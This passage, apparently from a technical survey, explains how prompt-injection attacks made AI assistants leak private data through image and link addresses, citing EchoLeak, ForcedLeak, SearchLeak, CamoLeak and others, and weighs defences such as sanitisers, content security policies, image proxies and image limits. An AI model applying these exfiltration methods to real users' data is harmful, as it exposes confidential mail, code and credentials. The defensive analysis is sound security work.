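Details of the fix are scarce. Reddy and Gujral write that Microsoft began stripping reference-style links and embedded images from outside content before the model reads it. They also mention reports of new options for keeping outside messages away from Copilot in some situations. They worked entirely from public material and ran no experiments.

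If it is accurate, the first change alone would not have been enough. An attacker doesn't need to include a finished link in the email, because the model can assemble one from a description in ordinary words. Rehberger had done something similar in Google Colab with fragments of text. Microsoft therefore probably also fixed the filter on Copilot's output, and may have closed the Teams relay, but neither Willison nor Reddy and Gujral describe such changes.

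Microsoft published an account of its defences in July 2025, a month after the EchoLeak announcement, but did not mention EchoLeak by name. Microsoft writes that it had deterministically blocked the markdown image leak that Rehberger reported, and had taken similar steps against "certain untrusted links". It adds that it deals with the general class of each reported problem, including variants. That is the right policy, but EchoLeak casts doubt on how thoroughly Microsoft applied it, because the variant that Copilot's filter missed could be found in an ordinary guide to markdown.

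EchoLeak is listed in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities as CVE-2025-32711. The copy of the entry at GCVE (2025) shows a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database. Both scores are based on an attack that needs no action from the user and exposes highly confidential data. Microsoft's score is higher because Microsoft also counted effects beyond Copilot and a small risk of altered data. The entry classifies the flaw as a failure to neutralise special elements in output that another component will use. Here, the output was the model's markdown and the other component was the renderer.

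Nobody has reported a real theft through EchoLeak. When Microsoft disclosed the flaw, it said attackers had not exploited it, and Ravia writes that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. The US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded the exploitation status as "none" on 14 June 2025, three days after the announcement. CISA's judgement was early, however, and the other two statements rest on Microsoft's word. Microsoft was in a good position to check, since requests through the Teams relay passed through its own servers, but neither Ravia nor SC Media explains how it checked. In their subtitle, Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first "real-world" exploit of its type, which is accurate in that the product was real but could suggest that criminals had used the exploit.

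### HTML image tags in Google AI Studio

Google had a similar mismatch the year before in AI Studio, its website for developers to try out Gemini models. It had already dealt with a leak through markdown images there. When Rehberger tested the site again in the summer of 2024, markdown tricks worked only occasionally, but when he had the model write an HTML image tag, the site displayed the image. Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio* calls this a regression or a bypass and adds that the gap might have existed all along.

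In Rehberger's demonstration, a manager uploads a set of performance reviews for analysis, and one employee has hidden instructions in his own review. They make the model summarise each of the other reviews and put each summary in the address of a separate image. Using several images allowed the attack to send far more data than a single address could hold. AI Studio had no CSP at the time, so the browser loaded each image from Rehberger's server once its tag was on the page.

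He also showed that the instructions could come from the frames of a video. A filter that searches incoming documents for suspicious markdown would find nothing to remove from a video, but a sanitiser that runs on the model's answer would still encounter the same image tag.

Rehberger got no date for a fix through Google's official channel for security reports. He then contacted Logan Kilpatrick, who worked on AI Studio, publicly on X. Within 24 hours, AI Studio was showing image tags as text. This technique, called escaping, works against any HTML tag, so the programmer doesn't have to list the dangerous ones.

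Many websites already have an HTML sanitiser, but it may not cover this case. Most are designed to stop script injection, in which an attacker gets a web page to run a program in another visitor's browser. They remove script tags, along with attributes and special addresses that can start a program. An ordinary image from an ordinary web address contains none of these, and these sanitisers normally leave it in place because people like to post pictures.

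GitHub's markdown dialect, for example, disables several tags, including those for scripts, styles and embedded pages, but not the image tag. This is sensible on a site where people write their own posts, because an image's address contains only what the person posting it put there. In a chat with an assistant, the address may contain data that the user never meant to send, and the browser leaks it by loading the image, without running any code.

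The same assumption appears in advice about EchoLeak. Among other measures, Reddy and Gujral recommend reducing the model's output to a safe subset of markdown and HTML that includes "plain images". This alone would have left EchoLeak's image on the page, so their other recommendations, such as a strict CSP, would have to stop it. A sanitiser meant to prevent exfiltration needs to check instead whether displaying each element makes the user's device contact another server. Stylesheets and fonts can do that as well as images.

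### Five formats at once in Antigravity

An attacker who doesn't know which forms a product filters can try several in the same answer. Odson and Morris did this in their attack on Antigravity. Their hidden instructions called for five forms of the image with the key in its address. Two used markdown (a linked image and a reference-style image) and three used HTML (a plain image tag, a figure with a caption, and an image wrapped in a link).

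Odson and Morris explain that renderers and sanitisers treat these formats differently, and that the attacker needs only one to load. Their server's log shows that a request with the key arrived, but they do not report which format produced it, so the test cannot show whether Antigravity filtered any of the five. It does show that a partial filter offers little protection, because the attacker can try four extra formats by adding a few lines of text, and a filter that stops four of the five still lets the key out.

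### Gemini's sanitiser

*Mitigating URL-based Exfiltration in Gemini*, a post on Bug Hunters, Google's site for reporting security flaws, describes a sanitiser design for the Gemini assistant that addresses most of these problems. The sanitiser parses the model's markdown on Google's servers, removes external images, converts every form of link to a single form, and escapes any HTML in the answer.

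Filtering on the server lets Google apply the same rules before the answer reaches any of Gemini's apps. If each app did its own filtering, Google would have to keep several sanitisers up to date, and an attacker could look for the weakest.

Converting links to a single form deals with the mistake in Copilot. Suppose a hijacked Gemini writes Dana a reference-style link. The parser looks up the label to find the address, and the sanitiser applies its rules to that address. If the link passes, the software rewrites it in the standard form, so the app's renderer never receives the reference-style version. This also makes the parser and renderer less likely to disagree, since the renderer has to interpret only the simple markdown that the sanitiser wrote. But if the parser mistakes a link for plain text and copies it out unchanged, the renderer might still recognise it as a link.

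Escaping the HTML closes the gap that Rehberger found in AI Studio. In the Antigravity test, three of the five formats would have appeared as text, and the other two would have lost their images. A user who asks for an HTML snippet may also see it as plain characters, but people asking for code usually want that.

The sanitiser is weaker against links than against images because it has to leave most links working. Converting links to one form ensures that it examines every address it has recognised, but Google still relies on its list of dangerous sites, which misses new ones. Google also records where an address came from.

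Some outside evidence suggests that the filtering works. Researchers at Tenable tried to steal data through Gemini and found that it filtered or restricted markdown images and links. Some links led to a google.com address first, and Gemini cut some answers short and refused some requests when it detected an injection. The researchers did not try every possible form of markdown, so some may still get through. But they judged the display hard enough to get past that they sent the data through Gemini's browsing tool instead. As with Rovo, the data left before there was an answer to sanitise.

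## Limiting which sites the browser may load images from

Microsoft's 2023 fix for Bing Chat included a new content security policy (CSP), which Rehberger noticed on the page. A sanitiser can remove only the images it recognises, but the user's browser applied this policy to every image the page tried to load. Embrace The Red reproduces the policy's list of allowed image hosts, all four of which belong to Microsoft: th.bing.com, www.bing.com, edgeservices.bing.com and r.bing.com. Bing Chat could still load the images it needed, such as the pictures it drew for users, but it no longer loaded any from Rehberger's server.

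### How the browser applies the policy

A website sends its CSP together with the page, in a part of the response that users don't normally see. Suppose the vendor of Dana's assistant wants to show its own pictures and those of a stock-photo library. It could send this line:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' data: pictures.assistant.example *.photolib.example
```

The `img-src` directive lists the allowed image sources, and similar directives exist for fonts, scripts and other resources. `'self'` allows images from the site that the page came from. `data:` allows images embedded in the page, which need no request and so can't leak anything. The last two entries allow images from a single host and, because of the asterisk, from every subdomain of photolib.example.

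If Dana asks what a certain office chair looks like, the answer might include a photo from pictures.assistant.example. The browser finds the host on the list and requests the file without examining the query string. If a hijacked model had added the door code to the query string, the code would go to the assistant's vendor, which already has it.

The image from collector.example matches nothing on the list, so the browser never contacts that server. Dana sees an empty space or a broken-image symbol. The browser also logs the refusal in its developer console, which programmers use to find faults. A policy can also name an address to which the browser should report refusals, which gives the vendor a record of attempted leaks.

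When an approved site redirects a request, the browser checks both the original address and the new one against the list. Suppose go.photolib.example is an open redirect, and the model writes an address there that names collector.example as the destination. The browser sends the first request because the host is on the list, and the photo library's server replies with the new address. The browser then stops because collector.example is not on the list, so the door code has reached the photo library but not the attacker. The browser would have followed a redirect to another approved site.

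Vendors can narrow an entry to one folder of a site, such as photolib.example/catalogue/, but when the browser checks the destination of a redirect, it compares only the host and ignores the folder. An open redirect on any approved site therefore lets an attacker reach every folder on all the approved hosts. Browsers ignore the folder to protect visitors' privacy, because a web page could otherwise use its own CSP to work out where another site redirects them.

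The browser can check only the requests it makes itself, so it would not detect the photo library's server fetching the picture from collector.example. EchoLeak used this kind of relay, the Microsoft Teams proxy that Reddy and Gujral describe.

### Advantages over filtering the text

The browser checks every image's address against the same list of allowed sites, whether the image was written as an inline image, a reference-style image or an HTML tag. According to Embrace The Red, Google AI Studio had no CSP in 2024, when Rehberger got an image to load there with an HTML tag. A CSP that left out his server would have blocked the image whether it was written in Markdown or HTML.

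Anyone who opens the page can also read the CSP's list of allowed hosts in the browser's developer tools, which is how Rehberger knew the four Bing hosts. He could not inspect the address check added to ChatGPT in December 2023. He saw that ChatGPT displayed some images and blocked others, and guessed on Embrace The Red that it might be looking addresses up in Bing's index, but he could not confirm this.

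Attackers can also read the list to learn which sites to search for a relay. On balance, the openness has probably helped vendors, because researchers found and reported most of the vulnerabilities described in this section by first reading the policy.

A CSP takes little work to add, yet some products still lack one. *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend* (veganmosfet, 2025) examined Dify, a platform for building chatbots that answer questions from a collection of documents. Dify's chat page displayed markdown images and by default had no CSP for them, so a hijacked model could make the browser load an image from any domain. PromptArmor demonstrated a similar attack that stole financial figures from an uploaded file. It recommended a strong CSP and blocking external images unless the user approves each one after seeing its full address.

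### What an approved site must not do

A CSP stops the leak only if no approved site will forward a request to an address the attacker chooses or let the attacker read what other people request from it.

An attacker who can read the requests sent to an approved site can steal data even if the site forwards nothing, which is easy to overlook. Many storage services let customers upload files and keep a log of who downloads them. If such a service is on the list, an attacker can upload a picture, get the model to add private data to the picture's address, and read the data in the log.

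Google's chatbot Bard, later renamed Gemini, failed this condition in September 2023, when Google gave it access to users' email and documents. Two groups of researchers found the problem independently. *We Hacked Google A.I. for $50,000* (Carta, 2024) describes how one of them did. Roni Carta asked Bard to display an image from an outside server, and nothing appeared. He opened the browser console and found Bard's CSP, which listed eight allowed sources for images. Seven of them covered all subdomains of a large domain, such as google.com, googleusercontent.com or youtube.com.

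Rehberger, working with the researchers Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, had run into the same policy and thought it looked broad. It allowed requests to script.google.com, where the Apps Script service runs its users' programs. Rehberger wrote a program that copied whatever followed the question mark in its address into his own Google document, and he found a setting that let people call it without signing in. He later used Apps Script against Colab's links as well.

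Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes the rest of the attack. The user brought a document with Rehberger's instructions into the chat, and Bard put the opening words of the conversation into an image address that pointed to his program. The browser allowed the request because the program was on a Google domain. The data went only to Google's servers, which stored it in the attacker's document. Bard was harder to steer than earlier chatbots, and Rehberger needed ten attempts and several worked examples before it filled in the address correctly.

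Carta and his colleague Justin Gardner used googleusercontent.com instead. Google gives addresses on this domain to some servers that its cloud customers rent, so anyone with an account could run a server that Bard's CSP allowed. Gardner set one up, but Bard now refused every request, apparently because a filter looked for that domain in the text. They disguised part of the domain's name and placed the address behind a redirect page on www.google.com. The browser checked the redirect page and then its destination, found both on the list, and sent the text of an email to Gardner's server.

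An alternative spelling got past the filter on Bard's input, which is how text filters usually fail. The CSP worked as Google had written it, but its list of allowed sites was flawed. Google paid Carta and Gardner a $20,000 reward, plus $1,337 for one of the best finds of its bug-hunting event.

Google confirmed on 19 October 2023 that it had fixed the leak Rehberger reported a month earlier. Rehberger saw that the CSP was unchanged and that images still appeared, so he inferred that Google had begun to filter data out of image addresses. Removing google.com from the policy would probably have been difficult, since Bard showed pictures and other material from many Google services.

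A much narrower list than Bard's can fail for the same reason, which is that an approved host lets strangers collect data through it. In January 2026 Willison described a leak in the assistant of the email program Superhuman, whose CSP allowed images from docs.google.com. That single host also serves Google Forms, which saves data sent in the same kind of web request a browser makes to load an image. One malicious email could make the assistant submit the contents of dozens of other messages to the attacker's form. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and fixed the flaw.

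### ForcedLeak and the lapsed domain

A CSP lists sites by domain name, and a domain's owner can change. In 2025 the security company Noma found that the CSP of Agentforce, Salesforce's system for AI agents that work with customer records, still allowed a domain that Salesforce no longer owned.

The ForcedLeak attack began with a web form that companies use to collect potential customers' details. ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* notes that the form's description field accepts up to 42,000 characters, which leaves plenty of room for hidden instructions. When an employee later asked Agentforce about the enquiry, the agent could follow those instructions, look up other customers' email addresses and put them in an image URL.

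The browser would load that image only from a list of approved sites, but the list included my-salesforce-cms.com, whose registration had expired. According to BeyondMachines, the researchers bought the domain for $5, after which the browser would send the data to them. Salesforce Ben quotes Noma calling the domain a "trusted exfiltration channel".

An attacker needs little skill to find such a gap. The list is public, and a registrar's website shows whether each domain is for sale. For the same reason, a vendor can easily automate the check and run it every day.

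Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce deployed its fix on 8 September, according to Nudge Security's timeline. Salesforce took back the domain and began enforcing a list of trusted addresses on what its agents produce. In a statement in The Hacker News (2025), Salesforce promised that the services behind Agentforce will not call or generate malicious links. The new control therefore covers links, unlike a CSP's image rules. However, it also relies on a list of names, so it too would have approved the lapsed domain if someone had left that domain on the list. Noma adds that the new controls should help Salesforce manage its trusted domains.

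### SearchLeak

In June 2026 the security company Varonis published an attack that got past both a sanitiser and a CSP in Microsoft 365 Copilot's Enterprise Search, which finds emails, meetings and files inside a company. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) explains how the attack combined three weaknesses, each of which would have been of little use to an attacker without the others.

The attack started with a link that opened the search page and ran a query contained in the link's address. Copilot treated the query as instructions and carried them out, much as Rovo did in the RovoBlast attack that Varonis published two months later. If Dana's company used Copilot, an attacker could send her such a link in a chat message. A filter that judges links by their domain would let it through because it leads to a genuine Microsoft site. If Dana clicked the link, Copilot would search her mailbox without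 her typing anything, take the subject line of an email and write an HTML image tag with that subject line in the address.

Microsoft had anticipated dangerous HTML in Copilot's answers. Once Copilot had finished writing, Microsoft's software wrapped the answer in a code block, which makes a browser show tags as plain text. Until then, the page displayed the answer as it arrived and rendered any HTML in it. The browser therefore requested the image as soon as it reached the image tag, while Copilot was still writing. When the answer was complete, the software turned the tag into text, and Dana would have seen code where the image had been.

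Programmers call this a race condition, because the result depends on which of two processes finishes first. Here the browser needed only a moment to send a request, while the sanitiser waited for the rest of the answer.

The CSP still blocked the page from loading images from the attacker's server, but it allowed every host under bing.com. Bing has a search-by-image feature in which its servers fetch and analyse a picture from an address the user supplies. The image address in Copilot's answer pointed to this feature and named a picture on the attacker's server, with the subject line in the path. Dana's browser would contact Bing, and Bing would request the picture from the attacker's server. The attacker's log would then show a request from one of Microsoft's machines, including the subject line.

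Bing Chat's short 2023 list of allowed image hosts included www.bing.com, which later served as the relay in SearchLeak. Nobody seems to have reported a relay there at the time, and the image search may have worked differently then. But the overlap suggests that it is hard to keep an approved site safe. Fetching images is an ordinary feature of an image search, and the people who build it have no particular reason to know that Copilot's CSP depends on their host.

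In Taler's published example, the attacker gets only an email's subject line. Even that can be harmful, because many services put login codes in subject lines, and a code often remains valid for several minutes. Taler argues that the same method could reach the contents of emails, meeting notes, and files in SharePoint and OneDrive, because Copilot can access everything that the person who clicked can.

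Microsoft catalogued the flaw as CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June and rated it critical on its own scale. The flaw scored 6.5, or medium, on the standard ten-point severity scale, which The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* attributes to the attack requiring a click. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers and said it had no evidence that anyone had misused it. Neither Taler nor The Next Web specifies which of the three weaknesses Microsoft repaired. Repairing any one of them would have stopped this attack but left the other two available for later attacks.

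Microsoft had already dealt with the first weakness in the consumer version of Copilot. Taler had used a similar link there in an attack called Reprompt, which Varonis reported in August 2025 and Microsoft patched in January 2026. He writes that he was surprised that the technique worked again in the business version, which is supposed to have more safeguards.

### Cleaning each piece before displaying it

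Nobody can undo a request after the browser has sent it, so a sanitiser must clean each piece of an answer before the page displays it, as Taler recommends. Microsoft's code block would have stopped SearchLeak if the software had applied it from the first word.

The simplest way to follow this rule is to hold back the answer until the model has finished, so the sanitiser can work on the complete text. But Dana would then look at an empty screen while the model wrote a long summary, and chat interfaces stream their answers to avoid this wait.

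Sanitising each fragment of the model's output as it arrives keeps the stream going but can miss an image. A fragment may end halfway through an image tag, and the sanitiser recognises neither half as an image. Once the page joins the halves, the browser has a complete tag and can load the image.

A better method is for the software to hold back text starting at any character that could begin an image or an HTML tag. Once the whole element has arrived, the software checks it and either displays or removes it. Dana would notice at most a brief pause.

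Reference-style images complicate sanitising a streamed answer because an image's address can arrive long after its label. If the model writes the label in the first paragraph and the address at the very end, the renderer first shows the label's brackets as text, then redraws the paragraph with an image once the address arrives. A sanitiser that examined only the newest text would miss that image. It has to recheck the whole answer each time the page redraws it, and finish before the browser receives the result.

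The software can also insert everything as plain text first, then add formatting only for elements that have passed the check. If the sanitiser is slow or crashes, the user sees some stray symbols. Copilot's search page instead treated HTML as live until the sanitiser removed it, so any delay gave an attacker's HTML time to take effect.

A CSP has no gap of this kind, because the browser checks the policy before each request, even if the answer is incomplete. In SearchLeak, the browser checked the image's address in time but allowed the request because bing.com was on the policy's list of allowed sites.

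### ReLeak

Vitaly Simonovich of Cato AI Labs published three attacks, called ReLeak, on 3 December 2026, and one of them again used Bing as a relay. Faisal (2026) reports in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* that each attack began with an unread email and that Microsoft's defences against prompt injection blocked none of them.

The attack through Bing (CVE-2026-124115) leaked data in the address of an image that the browser loaded automatically. Antipov (2026) notes in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* that SearchLeak had used a similar channel but needed at least one click. ReLeak thus combined EchoLeak's entry point, an email, with SearchLeak's method of sending data out.

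Cato reported its findings between 29 July and 20 August, after Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak, so that fix evidently left some route through Bing open. Microsoft may have closed the feature that Taler used but missed another, or it may have repaired only the link or the streaming and left Bing unchanged. It fixed the image flaw on 15 November and has not explained how.

Another of the attacks used Copilot's ability to create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF documents. The hidden instructions made it save a document containing a link with confidential information in the address. Microsoft's servers process new files in OneDrive and SharePoint in the background, and they contacted the address while processing this one. In Cato's tests this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the employee never opened the document. A CSP could not have helped, because no browser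 was involved, and a sanitiser for chat answers would not have examined the file. Microsoft fixed this flaw, CVE-2026-124132, on 11 November.

The remaining attack sent data directly from the isolated environment where Copilot runs code, without using images or links. Microsoft fixed this flaw on 17 September.

Microsoft made all the fixes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install, and Cato knew of no customers harmed by an attacker. Cato's researchers had used other AI agents to write test cases, study Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempt. Attackers can automate their search in the same way, which makes a long list of approved sites riskier than it was when Carta and Gardner checked Bard's list by hand.

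Taler advises security teams to check their CSPs for any domain that fetches URLs supplied by users. For an entry like *.bing.com, they would have to examine every feature on every Bing host, and check again whenever Microsoft adds a feature or host. A vendor could avoid most of this work by approving a single host that contains only image files the vendor has put there and has no redirects, forms or programs. The chat would then show images from the rest of the web only if the vendor's own server fetched them first.

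## Loading images through the vendor's own server

A vendor that wants to show images from the whole web can approve one image host, its own proxy, and have the proxy fetch the images. GitHub has run such a proxy, called Camo, since 2010. Users could put images from any website into comments, and many of those images loaded over unencrypted connections, so browsers warned visitors about the whole page. GitHub (2010) acknowledged that people complained about the warnings. Camo fetched the images and passed them on over GitHub's own encrypted connection. In January 2014, partly for privacy, GitHub began sending all external images through Camo, including those that were already encrypted. GitHub's *Proxying User Images* (2014) explains that other companies would no longer receive information about a visitor's browser.

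### How Camo signs an address

When GitHub turns a comment's markdown into HTML, it replaces the address of each external image with an address on Camo's host. Go-Camo, a version of Camo that other organisations can run, comes with this example (shown here without the prefixes):

```
Original:  golang.org/doc/gopher/frontpage.png

Proxied:   img.example.org/
           0f6def1cb147b0e84f39cbddc5ea10c80253a6f3/
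           687474703a2f2f676f6c616e672e6f72672f646f632f
           676f706865722f66726f6e74706167652e706e67
```

The last part is the original address with each character written as a two-digit code, such as 68 for "h". Anyone can decode it. The 40 characters before it are the signature, which the website calculates from the original address and a secret key that it shares with the proxy. Changing one character of the address would require a different signature, which nobody can calculate without the key.

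When a visitor opens the page, the browser requests the proxied address from Camo. Camo recalculates the signature and rejects the request if the result doesn't match. Otherwise it decodes the original address, requests the image from its host, checks that the file is an accepted image type, and sends it to the browser. By default it stops after ten seconds, four redirects or about five megabytes.

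GitHub's *camo* documentation explains that signing lets GitHub ban or limit requests and clear stored copies. Without signatures, anyone could also have used Camo to fetch whatever they liked. GitHub did not design the signature to stop data theft.

### What the image's host still receives

If a browser loads an image directly, the host learns the visitor's network address and often which site the visitor was on. In *Asset Proxy Bypass using non-ASCII character in asset URI* (2023), the bug hunter afewgoats points out that the host also receives any cookies it set earlier. With a proxy, the host receives only a request from the vendor's server. GitLab's *Proxying assets* recommends a Camo proxy server because a stranger could otherwise collect people's network addresses by posting an image in a comment.

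The host still receives the image's address, however. The email company Fastmail had to clarify this after announcing its own proxy, and its *Better security and privacy through image proxying* now notes that a sender may still be able to tell who opened a message if the image's address contains tracking data.

Dana's door code would also reach the attacker if her assistant's vendor signed every image address in the model's answer. The proxy would find the signature valid because the vendor's own software had made it.

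A signature protects the data only if the software does not sign addresses that the model writes. The model can then use only images whose addresses were already signed. If the model adds the door code to one of those addresses, the signature no longer matches and the proxy fetches nothing. Go-Camo's documentation likewise recommends filtering addresses when signing them, and treats the proxy's own filter as a fallback.

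### Risks of running a proxy

A proxy delivers strangers' files from the vendor's servers, which creates new risks. In 2014 a researcher found that Camo, GitHub's image proxy, checked only whether a file's declared type began with the word "image". A file declared as both an image and a web page passed the check, and the browser could run code in it. GitHub (2014) responded by accepting only files whose declared type exactly matched one on a list, and by moving the proxy to a domain outside github.com.

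The proxy may also be able to reach machines inside the vendor's network that outsiders cannot. Go-Camo therefore refuses to fetch from private network addresses, including through redirects. Its documentation warns that this doesn't protect internal machines with public addresses, and recommends isolating the proxy from the rest of the network.

The software that rewrites addresses can also fail. GitLab's code left any address it could not parse unchanged. In 2023 afewgoats found that a single non-ASCII character in the address of an HTML image tag could trigger this, making the browser load the image directly from the outside host. GitLab.com's CSP did not block the image because it allowed images from anywhere. If it had allowed images only from the proxy, the browser would have shown a broken image instead.

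### CamoLeak

In June 2025, Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found a way to steal private code through GitHub's Copilot Chat, even though it had a strict CSP and signed addresses.

Mayraz began with a pull request, a proposal to change a project's code. He put instructions for Copilot in a hidden comment, which GitHub allows in a pull request's description. The project's owner received the usual notification but could not see the comment. When Mayraz opened the page from another account and asked Copilot to explain the proposal, it followed the instructions. Copilot has the same access as the person using it, so a stranger's comment could make it read that person's private projects.

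Getting the data out was harder. A link containing encoded private code worked, but the user had to click it. The CSP blocked images from hosts that GitHub did not own. It allowed Camo's host, but Camo would fetch only addresses with a valid signature, which the model could not generate.

Mayraz could get signatures because GitHub has a public service that converts markdown to HTML and signs the image addresses in it. But he had to submit each address in advance, so he couldn't include a secret he hadn't seen yet. Instead, he obtained a signed address for every letter and symbol he might need and put the list in his hidden comment. Copilot then spelled out the secret as a row of images. Each image was a single transparent pixel on Mayraz's server, so the user saw nothing unusual. Mayraz could read the characters in order from the server's log.

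A browser or proxy may reuse its copy of an image it has already loaded, so requests for repeated letters might not have reached Mayraz's server. He had Copilot add a new random number to the end of each address so that it would be treated as new. Legit Security does not explain why Camo accepted the longer addresses, but the signature evidently did not cover the added part. Camo presumably did not pass that part on to his server, because otherwise he could have put the secret there instead of using a separate address for each letter.

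In one demonstration, Mayraz extracted the description of an unpatched security flaw from a private project. In another, Copilot searched the user's code for an Amazon cloud key and sent the result to Mayraz. Legit Security gave the Copilot vulnerability a severity score of 9.6 out of 10.

According to SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories*, GitHub told Mayraz on 14 August that it had fixed the problem by disallowing the use of Camo to leak user data. Legit Security reports that GitHub did this by disabling all images in Copilot Chat. The attack became public on 8 October, the date of the press coverage collected in *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025).

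Disabling images was drastic, but a better signature would not have prevented the leak. Camo had correctly refused to fetch any address that GitHub had not signed. The leak occurred because the model could choose among signed addresses after it had read private data.

### How much a fixed set of addresses can leak

The amount of data that can leak this way has an upper limit. Information is measured in bits, and one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. A secret with N equally likely values contains log2(N) bits, the number of times you must double 1 to reach N.

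Suppose an attacker has n addresses that the server can tell apart. One request can be any of the n. A second request again has n possibilities, which makes n × n sequences of two, and r requests can form n^r sequences. If the requests arrive in order, the attacker therefore learns at most

log2(n^r) = r × log2(n) bits.

*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) gives the same limit of log2(k) bits for a single request that chooses among k addresses. The paper is about AI agents that choose which web pages to open, but the same arithmetic applies to images.

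With 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, a request carries at most about 5.17 bits. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or 19.93 bits. Three requests can form only 46,656 sequences, but four can form 1,679,616, so four images are enough in principle. An attacker who wants simple instructions would have the model spell out the code with six images, one per digit, using only ten of the 36 addresses.

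### Caching and lost order

If the proxy keeps a copy of each image, never requests the same address twice, and sends its requests in no reliable order, the attacker learns only whether each address was requested. The order can be unreliable when a browser loads several images at once. Each address then carries at most one bit, so 36 addresses can carry at most 36 bits, however many images the model writes.

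This stops the attacker from reliably spelling out a code with one address for each of the ten digits. If the code is 404417, the attacker sees requests only for 0, 1, 4 and 7, and 1,560 different codes use exactly those digits. But the attacker can instead use 60 addresses, one for each digit in each position, so that one means "the first digit is 4" and another means "the second digit is 0". Six requests then reveal the code, even if they arrive out of order and no address is requested twice. The attacker could also write the code as a binary number and use only 20 addresses, one for each binary digit.

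A random 40-character key drawn from 64 symbols contains 240 bits, so sending it would take 47 ordered requests with 36 addresses, and it cannot fit into 36 bits. Caching therefore protects long keys and documents much better than login codes, unless the attacker can supply hundreds of addresses.

Ordinary caches are also easy to get around. According to GitHub's documentation, people whose images are not updating should have their server send a "no-cache" instruction, and an attacker's server can do the same. A vendor that wants its cache to limit leaks would have to keep each copy regardless of the image host's caching instructions, and ignore or reject anything added to the signed address, such as Mayraz's random numbers.

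Attackers can also leak data from ChatGPT one character at a time. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger suggests a similar defense, either storing each response for a few minutes or preventing the assistant from visiting the same address twice in a session. He concedes that some data could still leak.

### Limiting the number of images

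A vendor could also limit the number of images in each answer. The table shows the most that one answer can leak with 36 addresses. The figures for ordered requests are slightly higher than the formula gives because the model can also use fewer images than the limit, and the attacker learns something from how many it uses.

| Images allowed per answer | Bits if requests arrive in order and can repeat | Bits if order is lost and nothing repeats |
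|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5.2 | 5.2 |
| 4 | 20.7 | 16.0 |
| 5 | 25.9 | 18.8 |
| 6 | 31.1 | 21.2 |
| 36 | 186.2 | 36.0 |

A six-digit code needs 19.93 bits, so a limit of three images would keep it from leaking in one answer. If the cache is strict and the order of image requests is unreliable, a limit of five would be enough.

Even with a limit of one image per answer, an attacker can spread the images over several answers and recover their order from the order of the answers. Samoilenko's 2023 attack had already made ChatGPT add an image to every later reply. Four answers with a different image in each can form 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 = 1,413,720 sequences, again enough for the code. A useful limit would therefore have to cover the whole conversation.

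An attacker can also prepare more addresses, and with 1,000, two images in order can represent any six-digit code. Signatures make this harder because the model can't work out a signed address from a pattern and has to copy it from the attacker's text. Go-Camo's example signed address is about 150 characters long, so 1,000 would take up 150,000 characters. The 42,000-character form field used in ForcedLeak would hold about 280 addresses, so representing any six-digit code would take three images in order.

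No limit above zero prevents every leak. Even with a single address, the model can either show an image or leave it out, and a stranger could learn from that whether Dana's company is planning redundancies. For most conversations that risk is small, and a low limit would stop anyone from copying out a whole mailbox. GitHub had more reason to be strict, since Copilot Chat can read passwords and keys.

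### Fetching images before the model chooses

A vendor could keep showing images but change when its server fetches them. Liang and colleagues propose that an agent first download a fixed amount of material, without using private data to decide what to fetch, and then choose among the local copies. Outside servers receive the download requests but no information about the agent's choice. In their tests, this reduced an attack's success at reconstructing users' questions from 0.89 to 0.39, on a scale where 1 is perfect, so some information still leaked.

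With this approach, the proxy would download every picture in the price list when the email reached Dana's mailbox, before the assistant had searched for anything. If the model later included one of the pictures in an answer, her browser would load the vendor's copy. The interface would refuse any image without a stored copy, so the address containing her door code would never be requested. A list of signed pictures like Mayraz's would also fail, because the proxy would already have fetched them all.

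The vendor would have to store many pictures that nobody looks at, and the sender would learn that the email had arrived. If the server fetched the pictures only when a question led the assistant to the email, the sender would learn that Dana had asked something related to it.

The documentation for chat products with image proxies does not mention fetching images in advance. Mattermost, a workplace chat program that companies can run themselves, offers a proxy for all external images. According to Mattermost's *(Optional) Use an Image proxy*, the user's app loads images through the proxy. When an AI agent has written the message, the app loads the image after the model has seen any private data. The built-in version of the proxy keeps no copies, so repeated requests reach the image's host.

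Kagi, a search company with its own AI assistant, also has a proxy. Kagi's *Image Proxy URLs* describes proxied addresses for some API results, each with a cryptographic code that probably works as a signature. It is less clear how the assistant uses the proxy, but a user on Kagi Feedback reported that the model writes the original image addresses and the software then replaces them with proxied ones. If so, the protection depends on whether Kagi checks the model's addresses before signing them.

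The same user saw the browser also try to load the original addresses, and blamed the resulting errors on CORS, a browser rule that usually stops a page from reading another site's response but not from sending the request. If the user was right, the original hosts may have received the addresses before the proxy was involved. But this is one person's account, and a CSP could have produced similar errors by blocking the requests before they were sent.

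GitLab and Mattermost, like GitHub, have added stricter rules for AI output instead of relying on their proxies. GitLab's assistant Duo leaked private code through an image in 2025, and Willison writes that the fix allows only images and links that point to trusted domains. Mattermost's agents do not display links written by the model by default. Administrators can turn these links on, and Mattermost's administrator guide explains how to limit them to chosen domains.

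Mattermost also restricts images in its agents' posts, but it missed posts that showed the results of an agent's tools. The National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2026-3472 Detail* describes how an attacker could use images in those posts to send data to an outside server. OSV's *CVE-2026-3472* (2026) dates the entry to 26 June and rates the vulnerability's severity as low, at 3.5 out of 10.

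## ChatGPT's check of each address, 2023 to 2025

OpenAI continued to allow external images in ChatGPT but made the interface check each address before loading it. It introduced this check in December 2023, eight months after Rehberger reported the leak.

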